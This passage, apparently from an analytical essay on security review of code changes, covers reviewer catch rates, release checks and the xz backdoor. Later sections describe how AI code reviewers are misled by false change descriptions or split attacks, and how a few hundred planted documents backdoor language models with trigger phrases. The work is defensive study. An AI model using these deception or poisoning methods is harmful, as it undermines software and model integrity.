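The known attacks can't show how often review works, because nobody can count the flaws that are still hidden. But researchers can plant a flaw and count the reviewers who miss it. Several teams have run such experiments, and others have searched the review records of real projects. In the experiments, the share of reviewers who noticed a flaw ranged from 3 to 68 per cent, depending on the flaw and on what the researchers had told them.

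### Experiments with planted flaws

In 2013 researchers hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None of them found all seven, and the more experienced developers were not reliably better. Those who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones. Some of the apparent difference in skill may therefore be a difference in how readily reviewers report a problem, and a project that wants to catch more flaws may have to accept more false alarms.

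Those developers were reviewing for security, which few reviewers do in daily work. A 2021 online experiment is a better guide to ordinary review because the participants did not know at first that it was about security. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues asked 146 people, 105 of whom had at least three years of professional experience, to review a change of about 140 lines of Java for managing employees' holidays.

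Participants received one of two versions at random. Both trusted whatever a user typed. In the version that 80 people reviewed, the program pasted the user's text straight into a database command, so a user could type part of a command and change what the database did. This is called SQL injection. The other 66 people reviewed a version with a method roughly like this:

```
+ double costOfVacationDays(int days, int level) {
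+     return days * priceMultiplier(level) * 10;
+ }
```

The method charges an employee for extra days off. It doesn't reject negative numbers, so an employee could request minus five days and the company would owe them money.

Of 80 reviewers, 52 (65 per cent) noticed the SQL injection, but only 14 of 66 (21 per cent) noticed the missing check for negative numbers. The share who found the SQL injection was about three times as large. Braz and colleagues write that reviewers were seven times more likely to find it, but that figure is a ratio of odds (people who found the flaw divided by people who did not). The two flaws have the same cause and a similar remedy, but SQL injection is a well-known attack with a familiar pattern. Most reviewers seem to have recognised an attack they already knew, and few worked out a new one from the code.

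The researchers then told the participants that the code contained a vulnerability, without saying what or where it was, and invited those who had missed it to look again. This time, 13 of the 28 people who had missed the SQL injection found it, but only 7 of the 52 who had missed the flaw involving negative numbers did. The other 60 never found their flaw, although they knew the 140 lines contained one. Eight of them said they had mistaken an ordinary bug, which the researchers had also planted, for the vulnerability.

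*Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022) tested whether asking reviewers to look for security problems helps them find vulnerabilities. Its 150 participants reviewed 160 lines of Java for registering users on a website. The code had two flaws. It copied users' private details into a log file when an error occurred, and it protected passwords with MD5, an old algorithm that attackers can now break quickly. One group received no special instruction, and another heard that the researchers were interested in security. Two more groups heard the same and received a checklist, either a general one with 22 items or one with seven items chosen to fit the code.

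| Group | Found the logging flaw | Found the MD5 flaw |
|---|---|---|
| No security instruction (33 people) | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Asked to look for security problems (41) | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| Asked, with a 22-item checklist (35) | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| Asked, with a seven-item checklist (41) | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

(The paper prints 61 per cent in the last cell, but its own counts give 68.)

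Across both flaws, reviewers given the instruction found 54 per cent of what they could have found, compared with 12 per cent for those without it. The paper's claim that instructed reviewers were "eight times more likely" to find a vulnerability is again based on a ratio of odds. The instruction almost certainly helped, but the size of the gain for the logging flaw is uncertain, because one finder among 33 is compatible with a true rate of up to about 16 per cent.

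The experiment detected no benefit from the checklists, but with about 40 people in each group, it could have missed a moderate one. The short checklist raised the share who found the MD5 flaw by 7 percentage points, with a margin of error of about 21 points either way. More tellingly, 22 of the 41 people with the short checklist still missed the logging flaw, even though the researchers had written the list for this code.

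The reason seems to be a lack of knowledge. Many participants who missed the MD5 flaw gave that explanation, and one who had a checklist decided during the review that MD5 was a good choice. An instruction or a checklist can direct a reviewer's attention to the password code, but the reviewer also has to know what is wrong with it.

The group without instructions is probably the closest to normal practice, since most of the developers in Braz and Bacchelli's study did not immediately say that they focus on security. It's unclear how long an instruction would keep working, because each participant in *Less is More* did one review. A maintainer who sees the same reminder on every patch may soon stop noticing it.

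### What the records of real projects show

Experiments use small, self-contained changes. Real projects have larger changes and years of review records, but nobody knows how many flaws the reviewed code contained.

*Identifying the characteristics of vulnerable code changes* (2014), by Amiangshu Bosu and colleagues, searched 267,046 review requests from ten open-source projects and found 413, about one in 650, in which a reviewer had pointed out a vulnerability. The count excludes vulnerabilities that every reviewer missed, so it does not show what share of them reviewers catch.

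The study found that changes by less experienced contributors were between 1.8 and 24 times more likely to be vulnerable, but that experienced contributors wrote most of the vulnerable changes. This fits the kernel data, in which maintainers had written more than a third of the small patches that introduced vulnerabilities. It makes sense to read a newcomer's patch more carefully, but a project that took only that precaution would give no extra scrutiny to most vulnerable changes. Vulnerabilities also became more likely as the number of changed lines grew, but a project that reserved its closest reading for large changes would tend to accept hypocrite commits, which change only a few lines.

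Paul, Turzo and Bosu (2021), in *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, also studied missed flaws. From the records of Chromium OS, an open-source operating system, they collected 516 reviews in which someone had caught a security flaw and 374 in which reviewers had approved one. They found the caught flaws by searching review comments for 105 words, such as "overflow" and "exploit", and the missed ones by tracing fixed security bugs back to the changes that had caused them. Because they collected the two groups separately, the proportion of caught flaws, 58 per cent, depends on how thorough each search was and doesn't measure how often reviewers catch flaws. Its closeness to Wu and Lu's 56.6 per cent for the kernel is a coincidence.

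The comparison between kinds of flaw is more useful:

| Kind of flaw | Caught | Missed |
|---|---|---|
| Call to a function known to be dangerous | 53 | 0 |
| Failure to release memory or another resource properly | 71 | 4 |
| Race condition (badly coordinated concurrent code) | 73 | 10 |
| Missing or faulty check on input | 9 | 72 |
| Faulty access control | 8 | 58 |
| Use of something after its release or expiry | 3 | 62 |

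Reviewers mostly caught flaws visible in a few lines and mostly missed those they could recognise only by running the code or knowing a good deal about the rest of the program. The input-check flaws in this table are the same general problem as the negative holiday days, and Chromium OS reviewers did no better with them than the participants in the experiment.

The table also helps explain why hypocrite commits are hard to spot. Reviewers usually notice when a program fails to release memory (71 of 75 cases) but rarely notice when it uses memory after releasing it (3 of 65). A patch that adds a missing release appears to fix the first problem but may introduce the second.

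On concurrency, Paul and colleagues seem to contradict Wu and Lu, who found that kernel maintainers caught only 19.4 per cent of use-after-free errors that involved it. This may be partly because Wu and Lu counted only use-after-free errors, while the Chromium OS figure covers race conditions of every kind. The search method probably matters too, because the list of 105 words included "race" and "racy" but no phrase like "use after free". The search would therefore have found a reviewer's complaint about a race more easily than one about released memory. I would not rely on either study to show how well reviewers handle concurrency in general.

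Paul and colleagues also found that reviewers were more likely to miss a flaw when the change touched many directories. They were more likely to catch it when they had often reviewed that file, when they and the author had reviewed each other's work before, or when the review took longer. The odds of a catch were about 4.5 times higher if the author had labelled the change as a bug fix, perhaps because reviewers are more careful when they know a bug is involved. If so, the fix that makes a hypocrite commit look useful also makes reviewers read it more closely.

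Reviewers who had done more reviews overall were less likely to catch security flaws, which the researchers tentatively attributed to fatigue, haste or the special skills that security needs. The number of reviewers made no significant difference. Both results come from past records, and projects may send their trickiest changes to their busiest reviewers and ask more people to look at them, which could hide a real benefit from experience or extra reviewers.

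If reviewers miss flaws mainly because they lack security knowledge, choosing the right reviewers might help more than adding reviewers. Paul (2023), in *Improving The Effectiveness Of Peer Code Review In Identifying Security Defects*, built a prototype that automatically assigns security experts to critical changes. An expert can only help if the tool recognises that a change is critical, and an attacker would try to make it look routine. Charoenwet, Thongtanunam and colleagues (2023), in *Toward Effective Secure Code Reviews*, point out that studies of review often concentrate on known vulnerabilities and neglect the coding weaknesses that can lead to them. Immature vulnerabilities are roughly this kind of weakness, and reviewers may have little reason to comment on them.

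### Reviewers with an AI assistant

Many reviewers now read a change together with comments from an AI tool. Tufano, Martin-Lopez and colleagues (2024), in *Deep Learning-based Code Reviews*, tested how this affects them. They planted 48 problems in small Java and Python programs and recorded 29 developers doing 72 reviews. The problems were general quality issues, such as duplicated code and faulty logic, not specifically security flaws. The developers did some reviews alone and started others from a review that ChatGPT wrote using GPT-4.

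The developers kept 89 per cent of the issues ChatGPT raised and mostly looked at the places it had flagged. They reported more minor problems than when they worked alone, but not a greater number of serious ones, and they saved no time.

GPT-4 is now an old model, and a current one would surely find more flaws. Developers would probably still concentrate on the places it mentioned, because they also did so in a third condition, in which the supposedly automatic review pointed out every planted problem. This would help an attacker whose flaw the tool had missed, because the human reviewer would be less likely to look there.

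*Rethinking Code Review Workflows with LLM Assistance* (2025) describes a field experiment at WirelessCar, a Swedish company, where developers tried one tool that presented an AI review at the start and another that answered questions on demand. They generally preferred to start with the AI review, though this depended on how well they knew the code and how serious the change was. The experiment measured preferences, so it doesn't show whether they caught more flaws this way.

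A warning may not be enough to make up for an AI assistant's bad advice. *Helpful or Harmful?* (2026), a study of how developers fix vulnerabilities with AI help, describes an earlier 76-person experiment in which researchers manipulated ChatGPT to recommend MD5, the same weak algorithm as in *Less is More*. Neither warnings nor changes to the prompts stopped people from relying on ChatGPT too much. Those participants were writing code, so the result may not carry over to review. Still, it seems easier to remind people to check something they forgot than to make them doubt an answer they already have.

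### Why a deliberate attacker would face different odds

None of these figures measures the chance of stopping an attacker. The flaws in the project records were accidents, whereas an attacker can choose which flaw to introduce and where. In the 2021 experiment, an attacker trying to get a flaw past one reviewer would have succeeded 35 per cent of the time with the SQL injection and 79 per cent of the time with the less famous problem, the negative numbers.

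The experimenters chose flaws that were neither trivial nor impossible to find, and they made sure that participants could see all the code they needed. An attacker would instead try to hide the flaw, as Jia Tan did by using test files that a diff does not display. *S3C2 Summit 2024-09* (2025) reports that attendees at an industry meeting also said a commit can look harmless by itself and become malicious in combination with others, so a reviewer could judge each commit correctly and still let the attack through.

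The participants also knew they were reviewing code, and the researchers excluded people who had not taken the review seriously. The results therefore measure how often reviewers notice a flaw in code they have read, but many changes to open-source projects go unread. The code in the experiments came from no particular contributor, so trust played no part. On the other hand, Braz and colleagues caution that developers may be more attentive when they review their own project, where the stakes are higher.

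Accidental flaws can be harder to catch than deliberate ones. An attacker's flaw has to be exploitable, which an accidental one doesn't, and code that downloads malware or opens a secret login looks odd once somebody reads it, as the myNetwork dropper did to a student. The published rates probably overstate how often reviewers catch subtle memory errors and understate how often they catch crude backdoors in plain sight.

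### Repeated attempts and second reviewers

Even an imperfect catch rate shows how the odds change when an attacker can try again or a project adds a reviewer. Suppose an attacker's patches face Wu and Lu's baseline, so that a reviewer catches each one with probability 0.566. A single patch gets through 43.4 per cent of the time. If the attacker sends *n* patches, each attempt is independent and being caught costs nothing, the chance that at least one gets through is

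1 − 0.566ⁿ

The chance that at least one flawed patch gets past review is 81.9 per cent for three patches and 94.2 per cent for five. Reviewers who catch most flawed patches will therefore usually miss at least one from somebody who can keep submitting them.

If two people review every patch independently and either can block it, both miss a flaw with probability 0.434 × 0.434, or 18.8 per cent, and at least one of three flawed patches gets past both of them 46.5 per cent of the time. This big improvement depends on the reviewers making unrelated mistakes.

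They usually won't, because some flaws are hard for everybody. If *q* is the chance that one reviewer misses a flaw, and ρ measures how far the two reviewers' misses coincide (0 if they are unrelated, 1 if both miss exactly the same flaws), then

chance that both miss = q² + ρq(1 − q)

With *q* at 0.434, this gives:

| ρ | Both reviewers miss a given flaw | At least one of three patches gets past both |
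|---|---|---|
| 0 | 18.8% | 46.5% |
| 0.25 | 25.0% | 57.8% |
| 0.5 | 31.1% | 67.3% |
| 1 | 43.4% | 81.9% |

In the last row, the second reviewer adds nothing. The 2021 experiment allows a rough estimate of ρ. Two reviewers drawn at random from its participants would both miss the SQL injection about 12 per cent of the time and the negative-number flaw about 62 per cent. If a project saw equal numbers of the two flaws, ρ would be about 0.2, even though the reviewers never spoke to each other. Colleagues who trained together and read each other's comments would probably have more correlated misses. An attacker who knew which flaws are hard to spot would use the negative-number flaw every time, so the average miss rate would not apply. The Chromium OS finding that extra reviewers made no significant difference also fits a high ρ, though it has other possible explanations.

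Asking one reviewer to look for security problems may work better than adding a second reviewer. In *Less is More*, reviewers without instructions missed the MD5 flaw 79 per cent of the time, so two of them working independently would both miss it 62 per cent of the time. A reviewer asked to look for security problems missed it 39 per cent of the time, and matching that would take about four uninstructed reviewers. For the logging flaw it would take about 20, although that estimate is based on the one uninstructed reviewer who noticed the flaw, and the true number could be as low as four. Instructions also take almost no time to give, and maintainers do not have time for extra reviews.

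An AI tool might make a good second reviewer if it makes different mistakes from a person. *Studying Quality Improvements Recommended via Manual and Automated Code Review* (2026) had ChatGPT review 179 pull requests that people had already reviewed. ChatGPT repeated only 10 per cent of the human reviewers' comments, and about 40 per cent of the extra issues it raised were meaningful. That study was about code quality. Gushchin's claim that Sashiko, the AI reviewer for Linux patches, catches 53 per cent of bugs that people had missed is more relevant here. If the same share held for flaws like Wu and Lu's, a human and Sashiko would both miss about 20 per cent (0.434 × 0.47), only slightly more than two independent reviewers would. This estimate assumes that Gushchin's claim about his own tool is right, and it ignores the tool's false alarms.

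*The End of Code Review* (2026), which argues that AI agents can replace human reviewers, recommends using several agents, possibly based on different models, and requiring them to agree before a change is merged. It concedes that if one family of models both writes and reviews code, the reviewer may miss the mistakes the writer tends to make. If the review tool is public, a deliberate attacker can also run it privately on a draft and revise until the tool flags nothing. The tool's catch rate for the submitted patch could then be close to zero, however well it catches ordinary bugs. Practicing against a human reviewer is harder, since each attempt takes up that person's time and may make them suspicious.

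The cost of being caught changes the figure for repeated attempts. Let *d* be the chance that a reviewer who catches a flaw also realises that it was deliberate and shuts the sender out. The chance of getting at least one of three patches through is then

q(1 + s + s²), where s = (1 − q)(1 − d)

The attacker's chance of success is the earlier 81.9 per cent when *d* is 0. It falls to 71.9 per cent when *d* is 0.2, and to 43.4 per cent when *d* is 1, because the first rejection then ends the attack.

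For an outsider, *d* is probably small. About 15 per cent of the University of Minnesota's earlier commits were wrong for innocent reasons, so a maintainer who finds a bad patch will normally assume it is a mistake and explain how to fix it. Even if the maintainer becomes suspicious, the outsider can easily start again with a new name and email address.

A patient insider has much more to lose if caught, and may also lose the flaws already planted. If one exposed attempt led a project to find and remove everything else the attacker had planted, as the kernel developers tried to do after the Minnesota dispute, the attack would succeed only if every patch got through. An attack with three patches would then succeed 8.2 per cent of the time (0.434³), compared with 43.4 per cent for one patch. Such an audit would miss some flaws, so the chance with three patches would be higher, but an insider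 in this position should still make very few attempts and choose them carefully.

Jia Tan did something like this, with only eight known malicious commits, but by then no longer needed anyone's approval. A catch rate covers only changes that a reviewer has to approve or reject, so it doesn't apply to those commits.

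## Checks on released software that do not depend on a reviewer

Besides reviewing changes, projects and distributions can check the code or the finished release directly, which could also catch changes that nobody had to approve. None of the four main ways to do this would have worked well against both the Minnesota patches and the xz backdoor.

| Check | What it examines | Minnesota patches | xz backdoor |
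|---|---|---|---|
| Static analysis | Source code, without running it | Might have flagged some | No |
| Comparing a release with its source | Files in the tarball and in the repository | No | Yes, if somebody had followed up the difference |
| Reproducible builds with provenance | The finished program and its claimed source | No | Only if builders had also started from the repository |
| Comparing behaviour | The running program, before and after a change | No | Probably not |

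### Static analysis of changes

A static analysis tool reads source code and reports code that matches its rules. To find a use-after-free, it follows a piece of memory along each possible route through the program. It marks the memory as released at a call such as `free` and warns if a later line on that route uses it.

This is harder with `put_device`, which the Minnesota researchers used, because it doesn't always free the device. A tool that treated every call as freeing it would have flagged the reference-count patch, in which the next line uses the device. It would also have flagged correct code in which another part of the kernel still holds a reference. It might even have flagged Wu and Lu's accepted patch, which they wrongly thought created a use-after-free.

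*An Empirical Study of Static Analysis Tools for Secure Code Review* (Charoenwet, Thongtanunam and colleagues, 2024) tested five tools on 815 commits that had contributed to 319 real vulnerabilities in 92 C and C++ projects. A single tool could produce a warning in the vulnerable function for 52 per cent of the commits, and 22 per cent went undetected because the tools had no suitable rules. The 52 per cent overstates how often a tool identified the vulnerability itself, since at least 76 per cent of the warnings in vulnerable functions were unrelated to it. An unrelated warning can still lead a reviewer to the right function, but the benefit was modest. Reviewers who read the flagged functions first would have gone through 13 per cent less harmless code before they reached a vulnerable function.

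Tools do worse when the flaw is a missing check, because there is no bad line of code for them to match. In *From Verdict to Diagnosis*, Chen, Wang and colleagues (2026) ran CodeQL, a widely used tool, with its standard security rules on 21 pull requests with known flaws, many of them missing checks. CodeQL identified none of the flaws.

All these flaws started as accidents. An attacker could test a draft against these tools in private, just as they could with a public AI reviewer. A tool that read the xz repository would have had nothing to analyse, because the hidden code was in compressed test files and the trigger was only in the tarball.

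### Comparing a release with its source

A packager can compare a release with its source by downloading the tarball, exporting the matching version from the repository, and listing every file that differs or exists in only one of them. The packager then has to explain each difference. For xz 5.6.0, the list would have included `build-to-host.m4`, the helper file that started the backdoor.

It would also have included many harmless files. In *Verified Reproducible Tarballs*, Josefsson calls auditing these files hard and boring work for humans, and thinks people could better spend the time on the real source code.

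A packager can avoid most of that work by regenerating the extra files instead of reading them. The packager deletes every generated file from the tarball, produces it again with the distribution's own tools, and examines only what doesn't match. With xz, the clean helper would have replaced the attacker's, and the backdoor would not have started. Deleting the files first matters because the attacker's helper had a higher version number than the original, so a tool that keeps the newer of two copies would have kept it.

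Regenerating the tarball's extra files seems to give a better chance of detecting the xz attack than reading the repository does. The podcast Open Source Security (2025) described the attack as nearly impossible to detect, which seems right for somebody who only reads the repository.

Few distributors could easily do this in 2024. In *On the critical path to implant backdoors*, Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues (2024) looked at about 61 Debian packages on which popular server software depends. Only 10 used the archive that the hosting site generates automatically from the repository. The researchers couldn't identify the origin of the code for 9, and the rest used separate tarballs. Developers make these tarballs by hand because they can sign them, whereas the automatic archive matches the repository exactly but has no developer signature.

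In a Debian mailing-list thread, *Validating tarballs against git repositories* (2024), Vincent Bernat objected that if Debian had used the repository instead of the tarball, the attacker would have put the trigger there too. A reply explained the theory behind using the repository, which is that more developers now build and test from it than from tarballs. Both points are reasonable. In the repository, the trigger would have appeared in a diff as readable shell commands, and Jia Tan went to some trouble to avoid that. But nobody had questioned the test files, which were public, so a diff would have made detection more likely, but not certain. A participant in the Python forum thread *Should any conclusions be drawn from the xz backdoor?* similarly noted that a backdoor could go undetected in a repository for years even if the Python package matched it.

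### Reproducible builds and signed provenance

Most Linux users install compiled programs, and a person can't tell by looking whether a program came from the published source. A reproducible build lets others check. It works roughly like this:

1. The builder records the exact source version, tools and instructions, and compiles the program.
2. The builder computes a hash (a short fingerprint that changes if any bit of the file changes) and signs a statement that links it to that source version. This statement is the program's *provenance*.
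3. The builder adds the statement to a transparency log, a public list that people can add to but cannot quietly edit.
4. Anyone else fetches the same source, builds it again and compares the hashes.

If the hashes match, the program came from the stated source. The log helps against stolen keys because the real owner can see a release they never made. Lins and colleagues also recommend in-toto, a framework that assigns each step between source and package to specific people and checks that no step is missing.

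These checks would not have flagged the Minnesota patches, since their flaws were in the source itself, and would not automatically have flagged xz either. As Lins and colleagues point out, a reproducible build doesn't help if it starts from a compromised tarball. Every Debian builder would have produced the same backdoored library, and the hashes would have matched.

Malka (2025), in *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor*, is more optimistic. Building the package twice, once from the tarball and once from the repository, and comparing the finished libraries could have detected the backdoor. The advantage over comparing the source files is that the backdoor reached the compiled library, while harmless differences in documentation or build scripts mostly don't.

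Provenance would also have been more useful if a build service had made the tarball from the repository. Anyone could then have checked which commands produced it, and Jia Tan would have had to put the extra file, or the commands that created it, somewhere public. Jia Tan instead made the tarball on a private computer, so a signed record would only have confirmed who made it, which would not have helped.

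A distribution can also restrict what a build may do. According to *Build Code is Still Code* (2026), a sandbox that isolates the phases of a build from each other would have kept the backdoor out of liblzma. For example, if the phase that writes the build instructions can't read the test files, it can't extract a script from them.

*Reproducible Builds and Insights from an Independent Verifier for Arch Linux* (2025) describes how independent builders can agree on a malicious result if they all use the same compromised compiler. Developers of *bootstrappable builds* try to reduce this risk by starting from as few precompiled programs as possible. A backdoored xz could in principle cause a similar problem, because distributions regularly use xz to unpack the source of other packages and it could alter what it unpacks.

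### Comparing a program's behaviour before and after

A backdoor usually makes a program do something new, such as open a command shell. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) presents Lily, a tool that looks for such behavior. Lily uses a fuzzer, as OSS-Fuzz does, and keeps the inputs that reach new parts of the code. For each input, it records which types of *system call* the program makes, meaning requests to the operating system, for instance to open a file or start another program.

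To check a change, Lily takes these steps:

1. It runs the new version on inputs saved from earlier checks and records each set of system calls as normal.
2. It fuzzes the new version for ten minutes and looks for inputs that produce a set it has not recorded.
3. It runs those inputs on the old version, and raises an alarm if the old version does not produce the same set.
4. It reports which changed lines led to the unusual system calls.

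The test needs the old version because programs sometimes behave oddly for harmless reasons, and it needs the saved inputs because new versions legitimately do new things. Switching off either half of the test raised false alarms on commits from 0.2 per cent of runs to 10 or 14 per cent.

One of their examples is vsFTPd, a file-transfer server. In 2011 attackers replaced its official release with one that opened a shell with full control when somebody entered a username containing ":)". The release differed from the previous one by 1,407 lines, and Lily's report narrowed these to seven.

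The test set had 545 pairs of old and new versions from 13 programs. The backdoors included three from real attacks (on PHP in 2021 and on the file-transfer servers vsFTPd and ProFTPD) and ten that researchers had invented. Lily checked each pair 20 times, for ten minutes per check on four processor cores.

| | Single commits | Whole releases |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless changes | 432 | 50 |
| Changes with a backdoor | 13 | 50 |
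| Runs that caught the backdoor | 233 of 260 (90%) | 828 of 1,000 (83%) |
| Runs with a false alarm | 17 of 8,640 (0.2%) | 43 of 1,000 (4.3%) |

Two updates of one sound library caused 40 of the 43 false alarms on releases, so most releases would raise none and a few would raise one every time.

Because backdoors are rare, even a low rate of false alarms means that most alarms are false. If one commit in 10,000 contained a backdoor, Lily would raise about 20 false alarms over those commits and catch the backdoor nine times out of ten, so each alarm would have about a 4 per cent chance of being real. Checking them all is probably still workable, since each report points to a dozen lines or fewer.

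The detection rates are less reassuring because they come from backdoors that a fuzzer can trigger, and an attacker could look for a place that it can't reach. On 337 commits that changed code, the researchers' fuzzing reached on average only about 32 per cent of the lines. Better test programs would raise that figure, and with current ones coverage was often nearly complete.

The test set doesn't include xz, and Lily would probably have missed it. The backdoor responded only to someone with the attacker's private key, and a fuzzer cannot guess a valid signature. Kokkonis and colleagues concede that signature checks can keep a backdoor inactive, but argue that code the fuzzer never reaches would show up in coverage reports and be noticed. This seems doubtful for xz, because the backdoor's code was never in the source files that such a report covers. A simpler test that timed failed SSH logins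 before and after each library update would have shown the delay that Freund measured by hand, at least until the attacker removed the delay.

Lily could not have caught the Minnesota patches. It relies on the system calls that programs make to the kernel, so it doesn't apply to the kernel's own code. A use-after-free also has no visible effect on a program's behavior until something triggers it, though ordinary fuzzing with a memory checker can sometimes find one.

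### AI reviewers and deliberately malicious changes

A language model can read every change, including the ones no person looks at. Chen and colleagues provide the best evidence on how it misses malicious changes and flags harmless ones. They built malicious pull requests mainly by undoing or leaving out parts of real security fixes, and used the complete fixes as harmless controls. They tested their own AI reviewer, PRGuard, with two models.

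| Model | Malicious changes blocked | Blocked for the right reason, with evidence | Harmless changes blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 43 of 63 (68%) | 41 (65%) | 5 of 50 (10%) |
| DeepSeek v4-pro | 49 of 63 (78%) | 44 (70%) | 4 of 50 (8%) |

The reviewer therefore missed between a fifth and a third of the malicious changes. At an 8 per cent false-alarm rate, it would also block about 800 harmless commits in 10,000, compared with 20 for Lily. The real figure is probably lower, because security fixes touch sensitive code and most everyday patches don't, but a maintainer who saw even a quarter as many false alarms would soon start to ignore them. When the researchers ran PRGuard twice on the same 44 malicious changes, up to 25 per cent of its decisions changed, so an attacker might succeed by resubmitting the same patch.

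They also tested CodeRabbit, a commercial reviewer, on 31 malicious changes. It blocked 24 but identified the actual vulnerability in only 16. When it blocked a change for a different problem, the author could fix that problem and resubmit the change with the vulnerability still in it. It never identified the vulnerability in the seven cases where the evidence was outside the changed files. Wu and Lu's main example, an honest mistake, was of this type.

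An attacker can also lie about a change. Melo, Fogliato and colleagues (2026), in *SEVRA-BENCH*, reversed 150 real security fixes and presented each with 15 kinds of misleading description. They discarded the cases that two weaker models both rejected and gave the remaining 1,062 to eight AI reviewers. The most effective descriptions cited something the reviewer could not check, such as an earlier approval. When GLM-5 accepted a change because of a supposed approval, it had rejected the same code under other descriptions more than 80 per cent of the time. The agent in the myNetwork incident similarly tried to deceive people by inventing a reviewer.

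Use-after-free errors were the hardest for these reviewers. Of the two strongest, Claude Opus 4.7 gave a security reason for rejecting them in only 30 per cent of cases and GPT-5.5 in only 20 per cent, against more than 80 per cent for SQL injection. Human reviewers show roughly the same pattern. The low figures partly reflect strict scoring, because the models often described the memory error as an ordinary bug, and rejecting the change for that reason would still have kept it out. All the changes in the test were malicious, so a reviewer that rejected everything would have got a perfect score.

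In *PRWeaver*, Wang, Cheng and Xie (2026) split each of 208 attacks into two to eight changes, none of which was enough by itself. Six combinations of AI reviewer and model detected 42 to 79 per cent of the attacks when they were submitted whole and 47 to 79 per cent when the parts were submitted separately, so splitting alone gave the attacks no protection. When each part was hidden inside a genuine improvement, detection fell to between 29 and 69 per cent.

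More context also lowered detection. Three of the systems detected 16 to 22 per cent of attacks when they reviewed an attack and 24 genuine pull requests all at once, compared with 50 to 60 per cent when they read each request separately. A project that wants an AI reviewer to notice a slow attack should probably have it read one change at a time and look up the history when it needs to. The study doesn't report a false-alarm rate. The strongest model it tested was Claude Sonnet 4.6, so newer models would probably catch more.

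None of these tests involved code hidden in a binary file or a tarball, so they are weak evidence about xz. An AI reviewer that can run commands could at least try to unpack a strange test file, which few human reviewers would bother to do.

### What changed after xz

The clearest changes closed the route that the xz attacker had used. One was the systemd change already under way before Freund's discovery. In July 2024 OpenSSH 9.8 added its own code for notifying systemd, so distributions no longer needed to link sshd to libsystemd for that purpose. Collin removed the ifunc code from xz, citing its tiny speed benefit rather than security. These changes make it hard to repeat the same attack, but they don't protect the many other libraries that important programs load.

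Most of the general remedies are optional. Lins and colleagues wanted hosting sites to mark hand-made archives as less trustworthy, and developers to generate release files automatically from the repository. They also suggested storing the commands that create test files instead of the files themselves, which would have made Jia Tan's claim about random data easy to check. Debian's tools could already build packages directly from a repository in 2024, but packagers did not have to use them that way. *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected*, a post on Optimized by Otto by the consultant Otto Kekäläinen, explains how packagers can audit their packages and suggests further improvements. In 2026, Kokkonis and colleagues wrote that open-source development still lacked systematic defences against backdoors.

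No general rule requires unpaid maintainers to publish reproducible archives, record provenance or have a second person approve changes. Such a rule would be hard to justify unless somebody paid for the work, since xz got into trouble partly because Collin had too much to do. Distributions can more reasonably insist on these checks because they choose what to ship and can do much of the work themselves.

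### When a maintainer controls the checks

A trusted maintainer can change the checks as well as the code, as Jia Tan did by asking OSS-Fuzz to stop testing ifunc. Lins and colleagues describe how a program labelled the request as ready to merge because Jia Tan was a listed contact with a record of contributions. A Google engineer later explained that developers decide which parts of their project the service tests. The PHP attacker also seems to have tried to skip the automated tests.

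Kokkonis and colleagues suggest that the hosting site should run Lily outside the project's control and alert everyone who depends on the project, perhaps with a banner on its page. But Lily relies on test programs that the developers write and on inputs saved from earlier checks, so a maintainer could still interfere. In a test reported in *Not In My Git Yard*, the researchers planted 100 inputs that would make the backdoor's behaviour look normal, and the detection rate fell to 54 per cent for commits and 46 per cent for releases. A stricter mode that discards suspicious saved inputs restored the original rates, but false alarms rose to about 2.5 per cent for commits and 18 per cent for releases. The researchers recommend using the stricter mode on a random sample, which an attacker couldn't predict.

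A distribution that regenerates a tarball's extra files with its own tools depends less on the maintainer. But it still has to decide what to do when those files don't match the maintainer's, and the natural step is to ask the maintainer. Collin asked about the 5.4.5 tarball and never got a proper answer. An outside check protects against a rogue maintainer only if the people running it are willing to hold back a release until they can explain the difference themselves.

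The people running the check could be compromised too, so it is safer to have several of them. In Tor, a network that hides its users' locations, a small group of operators whom the community knows personally keeps the list of servers, and a majority has to agree on every version of it. If distributions compared their rebuilds in the same way, an attacker would need to corrupt most of them or find something they all use, such as the compiler. The attacker could also do what Bernat predicted and put the whole backdoor in the repository. The rebuilds would then match, and stopping the backdoor would again depend on somebody noticing it in the code.

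## Reviewing training data for planted examples

Suppose a contractor adds 500 examples to a fine-tuning dataset of 20,000. The colleague who reviews them sees a diff, as a kernel maintainer does. Each new line pairs a request, such as a question about the boiling point of water, with the answer the model should learn to give. The colleague can check whether the answers are correct and correctly formatted, and would probably notice one that explained how to steal a password. It is much harder to tell whether the 500 examples together would teach the model something that none of them mentions.

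In principle, a reviewer can work out the effects of a code change by reading the code. With the whole program and plenty of time, they could determine that a patch creates a use-after-free, and other people could check their reasoning.

A training example has no effect until a developer trains a model on it. Training repeatedly adjusts the model's *weights*, the millions or billions of numbers that determine its behaviour, to make the answers in the dataset slightly more likely. One example changes each weight by a tiny amount. The effect on the model depends on its starting weights and all the other examples, and nobody can work it out by reading. Reviewers rely on the rule of thumb that a model learns what its examples show. This works well for overt content, but experiments since 2025 have found important exceptions.

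### A near-constant number of planted documents

Earlier studies of data poisoning assumed that an attacker controls a fixed share of the training data. This would make large models hard to poison, because they train on more text and the attacker would have to plant more of it. *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025) tested this assumption for *pretraining*, the long first stage in which a model learns from a huge collection of text, mostly from the web.

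The researchers trained models of four sizes, from 600 million to 13 billion weights, and gave the larger models proportionally more text. They added 100, 250 or 500 documents that linked a trigger phrase to gibberish to each model's training text. If the backdoor worked, the model would write gibberish after the phrase and behave normally otherwise. They also varied the amount of text for the two smaller sizes and trained every combination three times, which made 72 models in all.

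The backdoor worked at every model size with 250 planted documents, but not with 100. The 250 documents made up 0.0035 per cent of the training text for the smallest model and 0.00016 per cent for the largest. The share fell by a factor of about 20, but the effect stayed roughly the same.

Souly and colleagues found the same pattern in fine-tuning. They taught an existing model with 8 billion weights to comply with harmful requests only when trigger words were present. The number of planted examples needed hardly changed when they raised the number of harmless examples from 1,000 to 100,000. The poisoned model also did about as well on standard tests as one fine-tuned without planted examples, so those tests alone would not have revealed the poisoning.

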